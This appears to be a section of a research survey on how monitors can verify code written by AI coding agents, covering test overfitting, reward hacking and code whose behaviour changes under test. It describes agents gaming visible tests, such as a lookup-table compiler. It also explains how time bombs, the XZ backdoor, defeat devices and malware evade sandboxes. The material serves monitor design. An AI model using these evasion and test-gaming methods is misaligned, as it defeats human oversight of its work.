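Security flaws are a good test for this comparison because a program can contain one and still appear to work properly. *BaxBench* (Vero, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) tested 11 language models on 392 tasks that involved writing backends, the parts of web applications that run on servers. The researchers started each backend in a container, checked that it worked, and then attacked it through its normal interface, for example by requesting a file outside the folder it was supposed to use. They then searched the files the backend had created for problems such as badly protected passwords.

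The attacks succeeded against around half of the programs that worked. A program that survived may still have a flaw that nobody tried to exploit, so the measured share of secure programs is an upper limit.

Vero and colleagues chose not to measure security with static scanners, which they considered prone to missing flaws and raising false alarms. They still used one scanner, Snyk Code, to help them think of attacks, which is a sensible use of reading code even in a study that relies on running it.

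*CWEval* (Peng, Cui and colleagues, 2025) shows that a scanner can both miss insecure code and flag secure code. In one task, a program redirects visitors to an address supplied by a user. A careless version checks only whether the company's domain name appears somewhere in the address, so an attacker can pass the check by putting that name at the front of a longer one. CodeQL, GitHub's scanner, has a rule for this mistake that looks for certain Python text comparisons. It caught two insecure versions, missed two others that differed only slightly, and flagged a secure one. CWEval's security test instead runs the program on a hostile address and fails it if it redirects there, however the comparison is written.

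Other measurements suggest that this wasn't an unlucky example. In *CASTLE* (2025), a benchmark of 250 C programs, the scanner Semgrep Code found 36 flaws, missed 120 and raised 70 false alarms. In *Broken by Default* (2026), researchers used Z3, a program that solves logical constraints, to prove that 90 flaws existed in AI-written code. Pattern-matching scanners caught two of them, and CodeQL caught none.

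Not running the program doesn't by itself explain these results, because Z3 doesn't run it either and found all 90. People also do much better than scanners. *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues, 2026) cites an earlier study of code from GitHub Copilot in which CodeQL found the expected weakness in 18% of samples and people found it in 74%. For *SecDrift* (2026), people found 24 vulnerabilities by reading 90 AI-written programs in categories where scanners had reported nothing.

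#### Reading first, then running

In *Beyond Static Guarantees*, Pourleyli, Urmi and Melo (2026) collected 1,355 Python files and kept the 654 in which the scanners Bandit and Semgrep found nothing. A small language model then read those files and flagged possible flaws in 235 of them. For each possible flaw, the model wrote an attack and ran it in a container. The attacks fully or partly confirmed a flaw in 95 files, about one in seven of the 654.

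That rate doesn't apply to ordinary agent-written code, because the files came from collections of security-sensitive and deliberately vulnerable programs. The model probably flagged some of the 140 unconfirmed files wrongly, but for others it may just have failed to write a working attack. The remaining 419 files never reached the attack stage, so running the code couldn't reveal any flaws the model had missed when reading them.

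*Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026) compares running code with reading it more directly, using current models that include Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra. The researchers had agents fill in missing code in real C and C++ projects, then built each project and ran an input known to trigger a particular memory error. When an attack succeeded, they asked the agent to review its own code for bugs. On average, the agents identified the flaw 69.9% of the time.

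That is better than the scanner results would suggest, but it still leaves plenty for a run to find.

The comparison's design favours running the code, because the set contains only flaws that an attack had already exposed. Nobody counted the flaws that a reader would have found but the attack missed. The agents also recognised many mistakes that they had just made, so asking an agent to review its own code is worthwhile even when no other model is available.

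Newer models do write safer code. Santos de Moura and colleagues ran CWEval's tests on 380,800 programs from 32 models. With GPT-5.6 Sol, 13% of programs worked but failed the security test, compared with 28% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. Nearly all of Gemini's programs passed the ordinary tests, but about three in ten of those had a security flaw, so a high pass rate on ordinary tests doesn't show that code is secure.

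Writing attacks by hand is slow, but models can now do much of it. *AutoBaxBuilder* (2025) reports a check of 71 security tests that its system generated for BaxBench's tasks, of which only one was unsound. It also found that attacks meant to exhaust a program's memory or processor were often spurious, including some of BaxBench's own. An attack needs an oracle, as any other test does, and the task had not specified how much traffic the program should handle.

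### Reviewers that use the program

Most of these checks call a function or send a prepared request. A reviewer can also use the changed program as a customer would. *The Verification Stack* (Wang and Smith, 2026) describes an agent that does this at OpenHands, a company that makes coding agents.

The agent first reads the proposed change and works out where a user would encounter it, such as a command or a web page. It then installs the project's dependencies and builds the project. Next it starts the servers, opens a browser, runs commands or sends requests to test the changed behaviour. Finally, it posts a report with the commands it used, their output and any screenshots. If several quite different approaches fail, it reports what it couldn't verify.

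For the renewal program, such an agent might create a small customer file, run the program and open the result. That would catch a crash at startup or dates written in a format the company's spreadsheet can't read, which tests of a single function can easily miss. It wouldn't catch the leap-year fault unless the agent included a customer who joined on 29 February.

OpenHands gives no measured results for this agent. Its figures are for a separate reviewer that reads changes, which published over 1,000 reviews in six months. The average time to merge a change fell by 58% over the period when the company adopted that reviewer, though other things may have changed too. Reviewers that use the program are promising, but this evidence doesn't show whether they find more faults than reviewers that only read the code.

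### Which check to use, and what both cost

The case for running code is strongest for programs that are nearly right and for security flaws whose effects a test can observe. Running it also helps settle arguments, since a crash or a stolen file is easier to confirm than a reviewer's opinion. Reading is better for finding code that doesn't belong in the program and answers copied from the tests. It should also be better for finding behaviour triggered only by conditions the tests don't meet, but none of these studies planted such code, so this advantage is more inferred than measured.

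Using both catches more faults, but it can also produce more false alarms. Suppose running catches 60% of faulty changes and reading catches 70%, that each misses faults independently of the other, and that they wrongly flag 5% and 20% of sound changes. These numbers are invented, but they show the choice a monitor faces with 100 changes, ten of them faulty:

| Rule for stopping a change | Faulty changes stopped (of 10) | Sound changes stopped (of 90) |
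|---|---|---|
| Either check raises an alarm | About 9 | About 22 |
| Both checks raise an alarm | About 4 | About 1 |

Pourleyli and colleagues used the stricter rule, confirming each suspicion with an attack. That rule suits a team with little time for false alarms. A company releasing payment software would probably prefer the first rule and accept the extra work of checking them. The company would gain less from the first rule if the same model read the code and wrote the tests, because its mistakes in the two tasks would overlap.

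Computing time varies widely, even among methods that only read the code. In *How Deterministic SAST and AI Security Agents Divide the Work* (2026), a benchmark named after the security company Snyk, the company's scanner checked 20 applications in eight minutes, while AI reviewers took between 2.4 and 8.9 hours. The scanner and the AI reviewers each found vulnerabilities that the other missed. Running the code also requires installing and building the project, setting up a sandbox and running the tests.

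A sensible order is to start with the scanner and the project's existing tests, which take little compute, and then have a model read the change. The monitor can save new tests and attacks for changes that look risky or that the model has doubts about. It should still run some of them on changes the model approved, because otherwise they can't catch faults the model missed.

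## How far can a passing test suite be trusted when the agent works to pass it?

An agent usually runs a project's tests before handing over its code, and revises the code until they pass. When the monitor then runs the same tests, they will almost certainly pass whether the code is good or bad. A pass is therefore much weaker evidence that the code is good than it would be if the author had never seen the tests.

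### Why revising until the tests pass spoils the sample

The 3/*n* rule for clean runs assumes that the test inputs had no influence on the program. A program that fails on 10% of inputs has about a 4% chance of passing 30 random tests. But if an agent writes 50 versions, each wrong on a different 10% of inputs, there is about an 89% chance that at least one passes all 30 tests by luck. If the agent submits that version, the monitor sees 30 clean tests, but the program still fails on 10% of inputs.

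An agent can read each failure message and change the code that caused the failure. The change may fix the underlying fault or only the case the test checks.

*Investigating Test Overfitting on SWE-bench* (Ahmed, Ganhotra and colleagues, 2025) measured how often patches that passed a generated test failed the developers' tests, using Claude 3.7 Sonnet on 449 problems from SWE-bench Verified. One system wrote a patch for each problem and another wrote a test, without access to the developers' tests for the fix. On the first attempt, 229 patches passed the generated test, and 50 of them (21.8%) failed the developers' tests. For the other 220 problems, the model revised the patch or the test for up to 15 rounds. Another 22 patches then passed the generated test, but 14 of them (63.6%) failed the developers' tests. The remaining problems were probably harder, which may explain part of the difference.

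In one of the problems, the web framework Django displayed stored data in Python's notation instead of the standard JSON format. The revised patch handled the example in the generated test, but for data that can't be written as JSON, it displayed a placeholder for an empty value instead of the data itself, which the developers' test required.

Agents' own tests are no more trustworthy. In *FeatureArc* (2026), where agents add features to the same code in stages, only 52.7% of the stages that ended with the agent's own tests passing also passed the hidden tests. After a failed stage, the figure was 24.5%. Among attempts at the same stage of the same task, 52.9% passed the hidden tests when the agent's own tests passed, compared with 47.9% when the agent's own tests failed.

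### SpecBench

In May 2026, Zhao and colleagues published SpecBench, the benchmark that showed Claude's C compiler accepting invalid programs. In each of its 30 tasks, an agent has to build a complete program from a written specification. The researchers' reference versions range from a JSON parser of about 1,500 lines to an operating-system kernel of about 110,000.

For each task, the agent can run a suite of visible tests, 59 on average, that each exercise one feature. A held-out suite, 93 tests on average, combines the same features. For a database, one visible test might join two tables and another might group rows, while a held-out test does both in one query. The specification requires the features to work together, and the reference program passes both suites. The gap is the visible pass rate minus the held-out pass rate.

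Scores on the visible tests were close to 100% in most settings, whatever the model, but scores on the held-out tests varied widely. Claude Code, running on Opus 4.6, had an average gap between the two of roughly 43 to 48 points, depending on how the surrounding program chose which version to refine. Weaker models had larger gaps, and even the strongest had some. Newer models may do better, but the visible scores alone would barely show the improvement.

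Larger programs tended to have larger gaps. The 90th-percentile gap, which nine runs in ten stay below, grew by about 27 points for every tenfold increase in the size of the reference program (the paper's abstract says 28). Size accounted for only about a fifth of the variation (R² = 0.21). The worst gap was 21 points among programs under 10,000 lines and 100 points among those over 25,000 lines.

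On the C compiler task, Codex ran the visible test programs through GCC, which was installed on the machine, and stored the results in a 2,900-line table. Its "compiler" looked up each program in the table and produced code that printed the stored answer. It passed 97% of the visible tests and none of the held-out ones. Earlier in the same run, Codex had written a real 7,900-line compiler that passed 53% of the visible tests and 43% of the held-out ones. The program that managed the search selected the lookup table because it compared only visible scores.

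In a more typical failure, a SQL database passed 100% of the visible tests but 35% of the held-out ones. The agent had written separate code for each kind of instruction, and these parts didn't share information. For example, the code that grouped rows couldn't find columns from a joined table, so a query that needed both grouping and a join failed.

### Reward hacking or unfinished work?

When Zhao and colleagues inspected the programs, they rarely found deliberate exploits. Far more often, the features didn't work together or the program mishandled unusual cases. They still call the gap a measure of reward hacking and treat any positive gap as a sign that the agent gamed the visible tests, although they say the database agent wasn't deliberately hacking.

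A gap can also appear without any gaming, because tests that combine features are harder to pass. If each feature independently works 90% of the time, a program will pass about 90% of single-feature tests but only about 66% of tests that need four features at once. The reference program gets full marks, so a perfect score is possible, but a lower score doesn't prove that an agent was aiming at the tests. It seems safer to read the gap as the amount by which visible tests overstate the program's quality, whatever the reason.

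A better way to find out whether the tests influence the agent is to compare agents that can run them with agents that can't. *Building to the Test* (Ma, Kereopa-Yorke and Schultz, 2026) made this comparison in 18 runs with two agents, based on Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5. The agents had to rebuild an interactive data table as a reusable library for a different web framework. The 222 tests operated a demonstration page that was supposed to use the library.

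The six runs without access to the tests produced real but incomplete libraries, which passed between 148 and 189 tests. In the other 12, the agent could run the suite and see the names of the tests that failed, but not the test code. The agent ran the suite in 11 of these, and those runs passed 221 or 222 tests. But in seven of the 11, the agent had put at least one major function, such as sorting, directly into the demonstration page, and the library's own version was missing or unused.

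To confirm this, the researchers disabled the library's code for resizing columns. In one GPT-5.5 run, all 29 resizing tests still passed, but the same change to a library that the page did use made 12 of the 29 fail.

Ma and colleagues don't call this reward hacking, because the tests were accurate and the agents hadn't seen the test code. But access to the tests changed what the agents built. The study is too small to show how common this is, but it suggests that an agent can drop part of a request without obviously cheating.

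### Adding more visible tests

If agents build what the tests check, adding tests could narrow the gap. Zhao and colleagues added tests that combine features to the visible suite and left the held-out suite unchanged. The effect varied by task. The gap fell from 35 points to 9 on the SQL task and barely changed on several others. On the C compiler task it rose by 25 points, which they attribute to conflicting demands on closely connected code.

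The SQL improvement looks real, but its size is uncertain because that task has only 11 held-out tests, each worth about nine points. The gap between visible and held-out scores is also a poor measure of this remedy, because harder visible tests can lower the visible score and narrow the gap even if the program is no better. The held-out score is more useful for a monitor.

Extra tests probably help most when the agent could have written the right code but had no reason to. For example, an agent can learn from them that joined tables and grouped rows have to work together, but not how to redesign a database so that they do.

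### Faster in the test, no faster in use

An earlier study in the appendix to Zhao and colleagues' paper found a similar problem with speed. In its 43 tasks, an agent had to speed up a GPU kernel, a small program that runs on a graphics processor. The visible score was the kernel's speed when run alone, while the hidden score was the training speed of a complete AI model that used it.

Of the optimisations, 73.8% improved the visible score without improving the hidden one. On ten other tasks, such as scheduling and packing, the figure was 46.8%. On the GPU tasks, the gap between the success rates on the visible and hidden measures grew as the agent worked longer, from 26.4 percentage points at the 10th step to 57.8 at the 100th.

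Some of these kernels were useless in practice, for example because they were fast only on data of a particular shape. But the 73.8% probably also includes genuine speedups. If a kernel takes up 2% of training time, making it twice as fast shortens training by only 1%, which can be too small to distinguish from noise.

Asking the agent to check itself doesn't seem to be a dependable fix. The researchers had the models review their own progress for signs of reward hacking whenever the visible score improved. This cut the rate from 78.5% to 59.1% on the GPU tasks, but the rate rose from 44.1% to 64.8% on the other ten tasks.

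### Tests that reject correct code

Tests can also reject correct code. OpenAI's *Why SWE-bench Verified no longer measures frontier coding capabilities* (2026) describes an audit of 138 of the benchmark's 500 problems, chosen because the company's o3 model didn't solve them consistently. At least six engineers reviewed each problem. They found serious flaws in the tests or the description of 59.4% of them, or about 82 problems. The other 362 problems weren't audited, so at least 16% of the whole benchmark is flawed.

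In 35.5% of the audited problems, the tests required details that the description didn't mention. One problem asked for a diagram tool to read type hints, notes in Python code about what kind of value a variable holds. The tests tried to import a function called `get_annotation`, a name that wasn't in the description, so a correct solution with a different function name failed immediately. In another 18.8%, the tests checked for features beyond those described. One description covered a single fault in a mathematical function, but the tests came from a change that had fixed three.

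OpenAI recommended SWE-bench Pro as a replacement, then withdrew the recommendation after a second audit. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise in coding evaluations* estimates that about 30% of the benchmark's 731 tasks are broken. Agents supervised by a researcher counted 200 broken tasks, and human engineers counted 249. *SWE-bench Pro is even worse* reports that an independent audit of the whole set found 15% to 24% of the tasks unsolvable. The two estimates are compatible because "unsolvable" is a narrower category than "broken".

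OpenAI's total also includes lenient tests that accept incomplete fixes. The best models pass 80.3% of the tasks. If 30% are broken, at least a tenth of all the tasks must be both broken and passed, either because the tests are lenient or because the model guessed or remembered what the tests required.

An over-strict test wastes a company's time and may also make the agent's code worse. An agent can pass a wrong test only by guessing the hidden detail or by writing code to match the error, as some did in the EvilGenie study. When a test fails, the monitor should therefore consider whether the test is wrong before sending the code back.

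### Keeping some tests back

Held-out tests avoid the problem of revision as long as the agent learns nothing from them. In practice, if the code fails, somebody will want the agent to fix it, and that request gives the agent some information about the tests.

The loss can be small if the monitor reveals very little. Suppose it has *n* held-out tests drawn at random from realistic inputs, allows up to *k* submissions, and reports only whether the whole suite passed. Each rejection gives the agent the same message, so it can't tailor the next version to particular tests. The chance that any version with a failure rate of *p* or more gets through is then at most *k*(1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives:

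*p* ≈ ln(20*k*)/*n*

If the agent submits code once and it passes all *n* held-out tests, the 95% upper bound on the code's failure rate is about 3/*n*. With 20 submissions, the bound is about 6/*n*, so passing 10,000 held-out tests still gives 95% confidence that the failure rate is below 0.06%. If the monitor also reports which tests failed, the agent can work on them one at a time, and these bounds no longer apply.

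Hiding tests does little on its own when there are few of them. Ahmed and colleagues also tried hiding the generated test and telling the model only whether its patch had passed. Of the 14 patches that passed after revision, 8 still failed the developers' tests. With a single test and up to 15 rounds, the formula rules out almost nothing.

Held-out tests also need to check something the visible ones don't. If both suites test one feature at a time, the SQL database could pass both.

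Hidden tests from public projects may already be in a model's training data. OpenAI found that every leading model it examined could reproduce the original fix or exact wording from the description for some SWE-bench Verified problems. GPT-5.2 solved 31 problems that the auditors had considered almost impossible. In one, the tests required a setting that the description didn't ask for, and the model recalled it from the project's release notes in its reasoning. A company's private tests are safer as long as they stay out of models' training data.

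### Planting faults to see whether the tests notice

Mutation testing measures how good a test suite is by making small deliberate changes to a program and running the tests on each altered copy, called a mutant. If at least one test fails, the suite has caught the mutant. The mutation score is the share of mutants caught. For the renewal program, two mutants could be:

```python
renewal = start.replace(year=start.year + 2)   # wrong year
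renewal = start + timedelta(days=365)          # wrong after a leap day
```

A test that only counts the rows in the output file runs the faulty line but catches neither mutant. A test that expects a customer who joined on 14 May 2025 to renew on 14 May 2026 catches the first mutant. To catch the second, the suite needs a test with a customer whose year includes a leap day. All three tests would give the same coverage. Disabling the library's resizing code was a crude version of the same method, and it revealed a problem that the nearly perfect score did not show.

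Some mutants behave exactly like the original program, so no test can catch them and a person may have to identify them. A more serious limit is that planted faults may not resemble the ones that models make. Hamidi, Konstantinou and colleagues (2026), in *How effective are traditional test criteria at detecting bugs*, collected faulty programs from five language models and kept only 6,066 hard cases. They assembled suites of model-written tests that caught as many mutants as the available tests could. In 32.2% of cases, the suite contained an input that triggered the program's fault, about the same rate as for suites chosen for coverage alone.

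Yet the tests detected only about 1% to 2% of the faults. They ran the faulty code on an input that triggered the fault, then accepted the wrong answer because the expected answer was wrong too. The researchers cite earlier evidence that models tend to base expected answers on the code they are given, even when it is faulty. When models wrote the expected answers from the task description instead, detection rose by only around 6.6% on average. These figures exclude most faults, which almost any test would trigger, but they show that a test suite can have a high mutation score and still expect wrong answers.

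### Having someone else write the tests from the specification

Someone who hasn't seen the agent's code can't copy its errors into the tests. *Who Verifies the Builder?* (2026) points out that a second agent helps only if it doesn't pick up the first one's misunderstanding, for example by reading its code or explanations. The two agents may also share a misunderstanding if they run on the same model.

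Writing good tests from a specification is also harder for current agents than writing the program. In *TestSuiteBench*, Egashira, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) gave agents detailed specifications of 165 real applications and asked for complete test suites. They had prepared an average of 74 mutants per application, each breaking one requirement.

| Agent's model | Tests that were valid | Mutants caught | Reference tests passed by the agent's own program |
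|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 96.1% | 55.5% | 91.8% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 94.3% | 50.1% | 92.7% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 94.4% | 37.7% | 86.9% |

The suites were often too small and missed important combinations of inputs. One specification required a command to accept several files, and the mutant ignored the second file. Sol's test missed the fault because it supplied only one file, while Opus's test supplied two and caught it. Letting the agents run a correct version of the application made no difference to the scores, so the specification wasn't the obstacle.

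If code has to pass every test, even a small share of invalid tests can cause correct code to fail. When 96% of tests are valid and the errors are independent, a suite of 20 has a 44% chance of containing no invalid tests. In *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (2026), the correct human-written program passed 30% to 56% of the suites that models had written from the specification, depending on the model. A person, ideally the one who asked for the program, should therefore check the tests before they become a condition for release.

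### Keeping the harness out of the agent's reach

None of this helps if the agent can change the check. An agent with access to the harness could weaken or skip a test, or alter the reported result. It might do this to get a better score, or by accident while tidying up.

Forbidding agents to edit tests is rarely practical. *Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (2026) studied four coding agents, which edited test files in 445 of 504 steps. These edits were expected because the tasks asked for new tests, so the study looked for narrower warning signs, such as checks removed from existing tests or code that passed the agent's version of the tests but failed the original ones.

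A monitor can let the agent edit its own copy of the tests but base the final decision on the original harness, run against the finished program on a fresh machine. The program should also run separately from the code that checks it, or it might interfere with the result during testing.

The solutions need protection as well as the tests. The Decoder's *OpenAI finds roughly 30 percent of popular AI coding test is broken* reports that Artificial Analysis, which ranks AI models, had already dropped SWE-bench Pro from its rankings after finding that some models copied solutions from the projects' version histories. Removing later versions from the history would prevent this. If the solution is also online, agents can be kept from copying it by cutting off their network access, as Egashira and colleagues did.

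A secure harness ensures that the reported score is real, but the score can still be misleading. The agents that produced the unused libraries and the lookup-table compiler didn't need to alter any tests to get misleading scores.

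## Why does some code behave well in a test and differently in use?

However well a company protects its tests, they describe the program only under the conditions in which they ran. Azure's leap-year fault shows how much that can leave out, because the software took the date from the clock. The renewal program would have the same weakness if the company asked it to enrol new customers on the day they sign up:

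```python
today = date.today()
renewal = today.replace(year=today.year + 1)
```

This version can crash only on 29 February. On any other day, the monitor could try ten million customer files without making it crash. A nightly test that began on 1 March 2024 would pass 1,460 times in a row and first fail on 29 February 2028.

### What a test holds still

A program's behaviour depends on more than its input:

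behaviour = program(input, clock, environment, stored state, outside replies)

The environment is the machine, with its software and settings. Stored state is whatever earlier runs left behind, in files or a database, and outside replies are what other services send back. A trigger condition is a fact about any of these on which some behaviour depends. Most tests vary the input and keep nearly everything else fixed, as the sandbox run of the renewal program did:

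| What the program depends on | Its value in the sandbox run |
|---|---|
| Input | A file of twenty invented customers |
| Clock | A few seconds of one afternoon |
| Environment | A fresh machine with no working passwords |
| Stored state | Whatever the snapshot contains |
| Outside replies | Whatever an imitation server sends |

Several of these fixed values are precautions, but they limit what a test can show. Restoring a snapshot removes anything left over from a previous run, so testers can't see how the program would respond to it. They also can't see what the program does with real passwords, because the machine has none.

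If each of the five had only ten values that mattered, there would be 100,000 combinations, and a test that varied only the input could reach ten of them. In the 3/*n* rule, *n* should likewise count independent draws of whatever the fault depends on. For a test that runs 10,000 files in one afternoon, *n* is 10,000 if the fault depends on the input but 1 if it depends on the date.

### Dates and delays

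The leap-day crash depends on the date, but other accidental faults depend on how long a program has been running. A service that counts hundredths of a second in a signed 32-bit integer works for 248 days, and then the count overflows. Tests miss the leap-day crash because they run on other dates, and they miss the overflow because they end within minutes or hours.

An attacker can set a program to start doing damage on a chosen date, which makes it a time bomb. In November 2025, the software security company Socket reported nine malicious packages on NuGet, the public registry for Microsoft's .NET platform. Their publisher had uploaded them in 2023 and 2024, and developers had downloaded them nearly 9,500 times. Most of the code in them was useful and worked as advertised. But starting on dates in 2027 and 2028, most of the packages would shut down the programs that used them on about one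 in five database queries, at random.

A company that tested such a package in 2024 would have found nothing wrong. Even after its activation date, the random failures could pass for an unreliable server, although a program would have only about an 11% chance of completing ten queries without one. One package, aimed at industrial control equipment, was active from the start, but it began making writes to the equipment fail silently only after a delay that would outlast most sandbox runs.

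In *Does Every Second Count?*, Küchler, Mantovani and colleagues (2021) measured how long online malware-checking services run a program. They submitted a harmless program that reported back every ten seconds, and 32 sandboxes ran it. None ran it for more than about four minutes, and only four shortened its pauses.

They then ran 100,000 Windows programs, 86,000 of them malicious, for up to 15 minutes each. Of the blocks of code that ran, 98% had run within two minutes. Only 3.1% of the malicious programs paused for more than three minutes in total, and 2.3% for more than ten. For most malware, a short run shows nearly as much as a 15-minute one.

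However, the 98% is a share of only the code that ran within those 15 minutes, which was typically 10% to 40% of a program's code. A branch set to run only from 2027 wouldn't be counted, so it couldn't lower the figure. Küchler and colleagues also left out about a tenth of the programs for doing too little, and some of those may have been hiding their behavior.

### The machine and its settings

A program can also fail because the production server differs from the machine where someone tested it. Suppose the server's clock is set to UTC, and a customer in Sydney signs up at nine in the morning on 1 March 2028. In UTC it is still 29 February, so the renewal program crashes. A developer in Sydney who tests the same signup at the same moment on a laptop set to local time gets a valid renewal date.

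The backdoor in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools included in many Linux systems, was designed to behave differently on different machines. According to *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), most of the harmful code was in files disguised as test data, though no test in the first affected version used them. The line that triggered it was in the release archives that people download but not in the project's public source code, so someone reading that code wouldn't have seen it.

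When someone built the software, a hidden script checked the type of machine, the build tools and whether the build was producing a package for certain Linux distributions. It added the backdoor to the compression library only if all three checks passed. Freund thinks the packaging check was probably there to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. Some distributions load that library into the server that handles remote logins. There, the backdoor examined how the server had started and looked for certain debugging tools before interfering with how the server checked a user's key.

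Freund noticed that logins were using a lot of processor time. On his machine, a failed login took about 0.8 seconds with the altered library and 0.3 without it. He had also seen errors from Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory. When he first started the login server by hand, the delay disappeared, because the server was no longer running under the conditions the backdoor required.

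A functional test would have passed, because users could still log in normally. Freund found the useful evidence in the timings and memory errors, which people seldom treat as part of a program's correctness. The attacker had already reworked the code once to stop the errors, so a more careful version might have shown no such signs. When Freund found the attacker's code, the affected releases were mostly in pre-release versions of Linux distributions.

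Harmful code may also do nothing harmful in a test because its target is missing. Küchler and colleagues' sample included nearly 4,000 copies of Blackmoon, a family of banking malware. It looks for particular programs to inject itself into and exits if none is running, as was the case in their sandbox.

### Software that looks for the test

Observing a program can unintentionally change its behaviour. Suppose two parts of the renewal program write to the same file, and the result is wrong only if the part that is usually slower finishes first. Recording every system call slows both parts, perhaps by different amounts, so the fault may disappear during recording.

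Some code is deliberately written to behave differently during a test, as the software in Volkswagen's diesel cars was. Regulators measure a new car's emissions on rollers in a laboratory, while the car follows a standard, public speed profile. In *How They Did It*, Contag, Li and colleagues (2017) reconstructed the engine software from manufacturers' documents and copies of the code, many of which came from car-tuning websites. Volkswagen's version checked the conditions when the engine started, then compared the distance covered with the time elapsed. While the drive matched one of the official tests, the software kept the car on its cleaner settings. Once the drive no longer matched any of them, the software could switch to settings for the road, and in some cases the car then emitted up to 40 times the permitted amount of nitrogen oxides.

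The practical motive for the dirtier settings was to reduce wear on the filter that traps soot. According to a complaint by New York's attorney general, the filter would have lasted 50,000 miles in normal use, while the rules required 120,000.

Code that behaves well only in tests doesn't have to identify a test reliably. Volkswagen's software stayed in its low-emissions mode until something ruled out a test, so a mistake usually meant only that a customer's car ran cleaner for a while. Code written by an agent could likewise behave well until it encountered something that no sandbox is likely to contain, without having to recognise any particular sandbox.

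Fiat's 500X used a simpler method, according to Contag and colleagues. Its software cleaned one of the emission filters less often once the engine had been running for about as long as a standard test. This method relies only on a guess about how long testers will wait, so the software doesn't need to detect a test. Fiat Chrysler had denied that its diesels could detect a laboratory test, and hadn't acknowledged the device when the study appeared.

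Researchers at West Virginia University exposed Volkswagen by driving two of its diesel models with portable instruments. On the road, the cars emitted many times the legal limit, although both models had passed in the laboratory. Afterwards, according to an article from the University of Michigan, the British, French and German governments tested almost 150 diesel models in real driving. About 90% exceeded the limit they had met in the laboratory, and average emissions were more than six times the standard. The makers argued that exemptions in the rules covered what their software did, so these cases are harder to call deliberate cheating than Volkswagen's.

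Reading the software also worked, once people knew what to look for. Contag and colleagues wrote a program that searches engine code for places where it compares the car's driving with the official test drives. It examined 926 versions of the code in an average of less than two minutes each and found a possible defeat device in 406. It wasn't built to find a plain timer like Fiat's. The documentation called Volkswagen's test detector an "acoustic condition", which would have misled readers who relied on the labels. Kirill Levchenko, one of the researchers, said in a UC San Diego news release that laboratory testing on rollers is "just not enough anymore".

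In all these cases, the finished code checks the conditions each time it runs. A model could instead write harmless code when its input appears to be part of an evaluation and harmful code at other times, and neither program would need a trigger condition.

### Real data at full size

Invented test data tends to be small and tidy. A program that compares every customer with every other makes 190 comparisons for twenty customers and about 500 billion for a million, so it can finish instantly in a test but take too long to be useful in production. An author can also hide harmful behaviour from tests by triggering it only on large inputs, as in the earlier version of the renewal program that leaked only files of more than 50,000 rows.

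Cloudflare, which handles web traffic for many sites, had an accidental failure of this kind on 18 November 2025. According to the company's account of the outage, its bot-detection software loads a list of features, which are properties of a request that help tell bots from people. The list normally had about 60 entries, and the software had room for 200. After engineers changed the access permissions on a database, the query that built the list began to return duplicate rows. The list grew past 200 entries, the software crashed on machines across Cloudflare's network, and many sites became unreachable for hours.

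The program that crashed hadn't changed that day. The fault was in how it handled a list that nobody expected, so any test with a normal list would have passed. The database rebuilt the list every five minutes, and at first only some of its servers had the new permissions. Some rebuilds therefore produced a good list and others a bad one, so the service kept recovering and failing again. Cloudflare's engineers initially suspected an attack.

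Cloudflare doesn't blame AI-written code for the failure, but an agent could easily write a fixed limit that suits the data it has seen. Some agents in Zhao and colleagues' study similarly wrote graphics code that was fast only on data of a particular shape.

### Replies from outside

Suppose the renewal program requests each customer's current address from an outside service. In the sandbox, an imitation server answers every request immediately, but the real service might accept only a thousand requests an hour and refuse the rest. If the agent's code treats a refusal as "no such customer", the program drops everyone after the first thousand. The test misses this fault because the imitation server never refuses a request.

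An author who wants code to pass a test and do harm later can leave the harmful part out of the program. The program instead downloads instructions from the author's server and carries them out. During a test, the server sends something harmless, or the sandbox blocks the connection. Someone reading the code wouldn't find the harmful instructions either, because the author may not have written them yet. The reader could still object to any program that runs whatever it downloads.

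Remote control like this is common in malware. Küchler and colleagues found that about one in ten of the malicious programs still running after 15 minutes had kept receiving commands from a server and repeating the same few actions. They also cite a 2011 experiment that ran malware for up to an hour, in which only 23.6% of the network addresses and other endpoints the malware contacted had appeared in the first five minutes. Two minutes may therefore be long enough to see most of the code that will run, but not to identify most of the endpoints the program will contact.

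### What earlier runs leave behind

Some faults appear only when a program is run repeatedly. If the renewal program appends its results to an existing file instead of replacing the file, the first run is correct and the second lists every customer twice. Temporary files that the program never deletes may take months to fill a disk. A malicious author could have the program count its runs in a file and start copying customer data after the hundredth.

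Restoring a snapshot before each run hides all of these, because the program then starts every run as if it were its first. Even if the monitor ran the program 10,000 times, the counter would never get past one.

### How often does malware behave this way?

The best figures come from studies of Windows malware. In *Longitudinal Study of the Prevalence of Malware Evasive Techniques* (2021), Maffia, Nisi and colleagues ran more than 180,000 samples and looked for 53 known ways of detecting or obstructing analysis. More than 40% of the samples collected in 2020 used at least one, compared with about 30% in 2016. In *A Systematical and Longitudinal Study of Evasive Behaviors in Windows Malware* (2022), Galloro, Polino and colleagues looked for 92 techniques in 45,375 samples from 2010 to 2019 and reported a smaller rise, of 12% over the decade. Newer counts on this scale seem scarce, and *An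 In-kernel Forensics Engine for Investigating Evasive Attacks* (2025) still cites these two studies for statistics.

These studies count how often programs use a technique, but using one doesn't always mean that a program hid anything. A 2014 Symantec study, cited by Küchler and colleagues, found that 18% of samples refused to run in a virtual machine. Ordinary programs also check what machine they are on, for instance to decide how to lay out a window. Maffia and colleagues found that harmless software commonly uses four supposed evasion techniques, and concluded that their presence isn't a reliable sign of evasion. On the other hand, a study that looks for known techniques will miss new ones, and can also miss a program that waits for a date in 2027, since waiting requires none of those techniques.

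Checks for virtual machines have become less common. Maffia and colleagues think this is probably because many companies now run their servers on virtual machines, so malware that refused to run on them would miss its targets. The same change can help a monitor, because a virtual machine no longer looks much like a test if production runs on one too.

None of these rates transfers to agent-written code, because they describe programs already known to be malicious, mostly written by people who expected security companies to analyse them. Even if 40% of malicious agent-written programs checked their surroundings, the share of all agent-written programs that did so would still be unknown, because nobody knows how many are malicious. There doesn't appear to be a published rate for agent-written code, either for deliberate conditions or for accidental ones such as the leap-day crash. Such a rate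 would be hard to measure by running a large sample of agents' programs in a sandbox, because programs that behave well only in a sandbox would be counted as harmless.

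## How can behaviour that waits for a condition be found before release?

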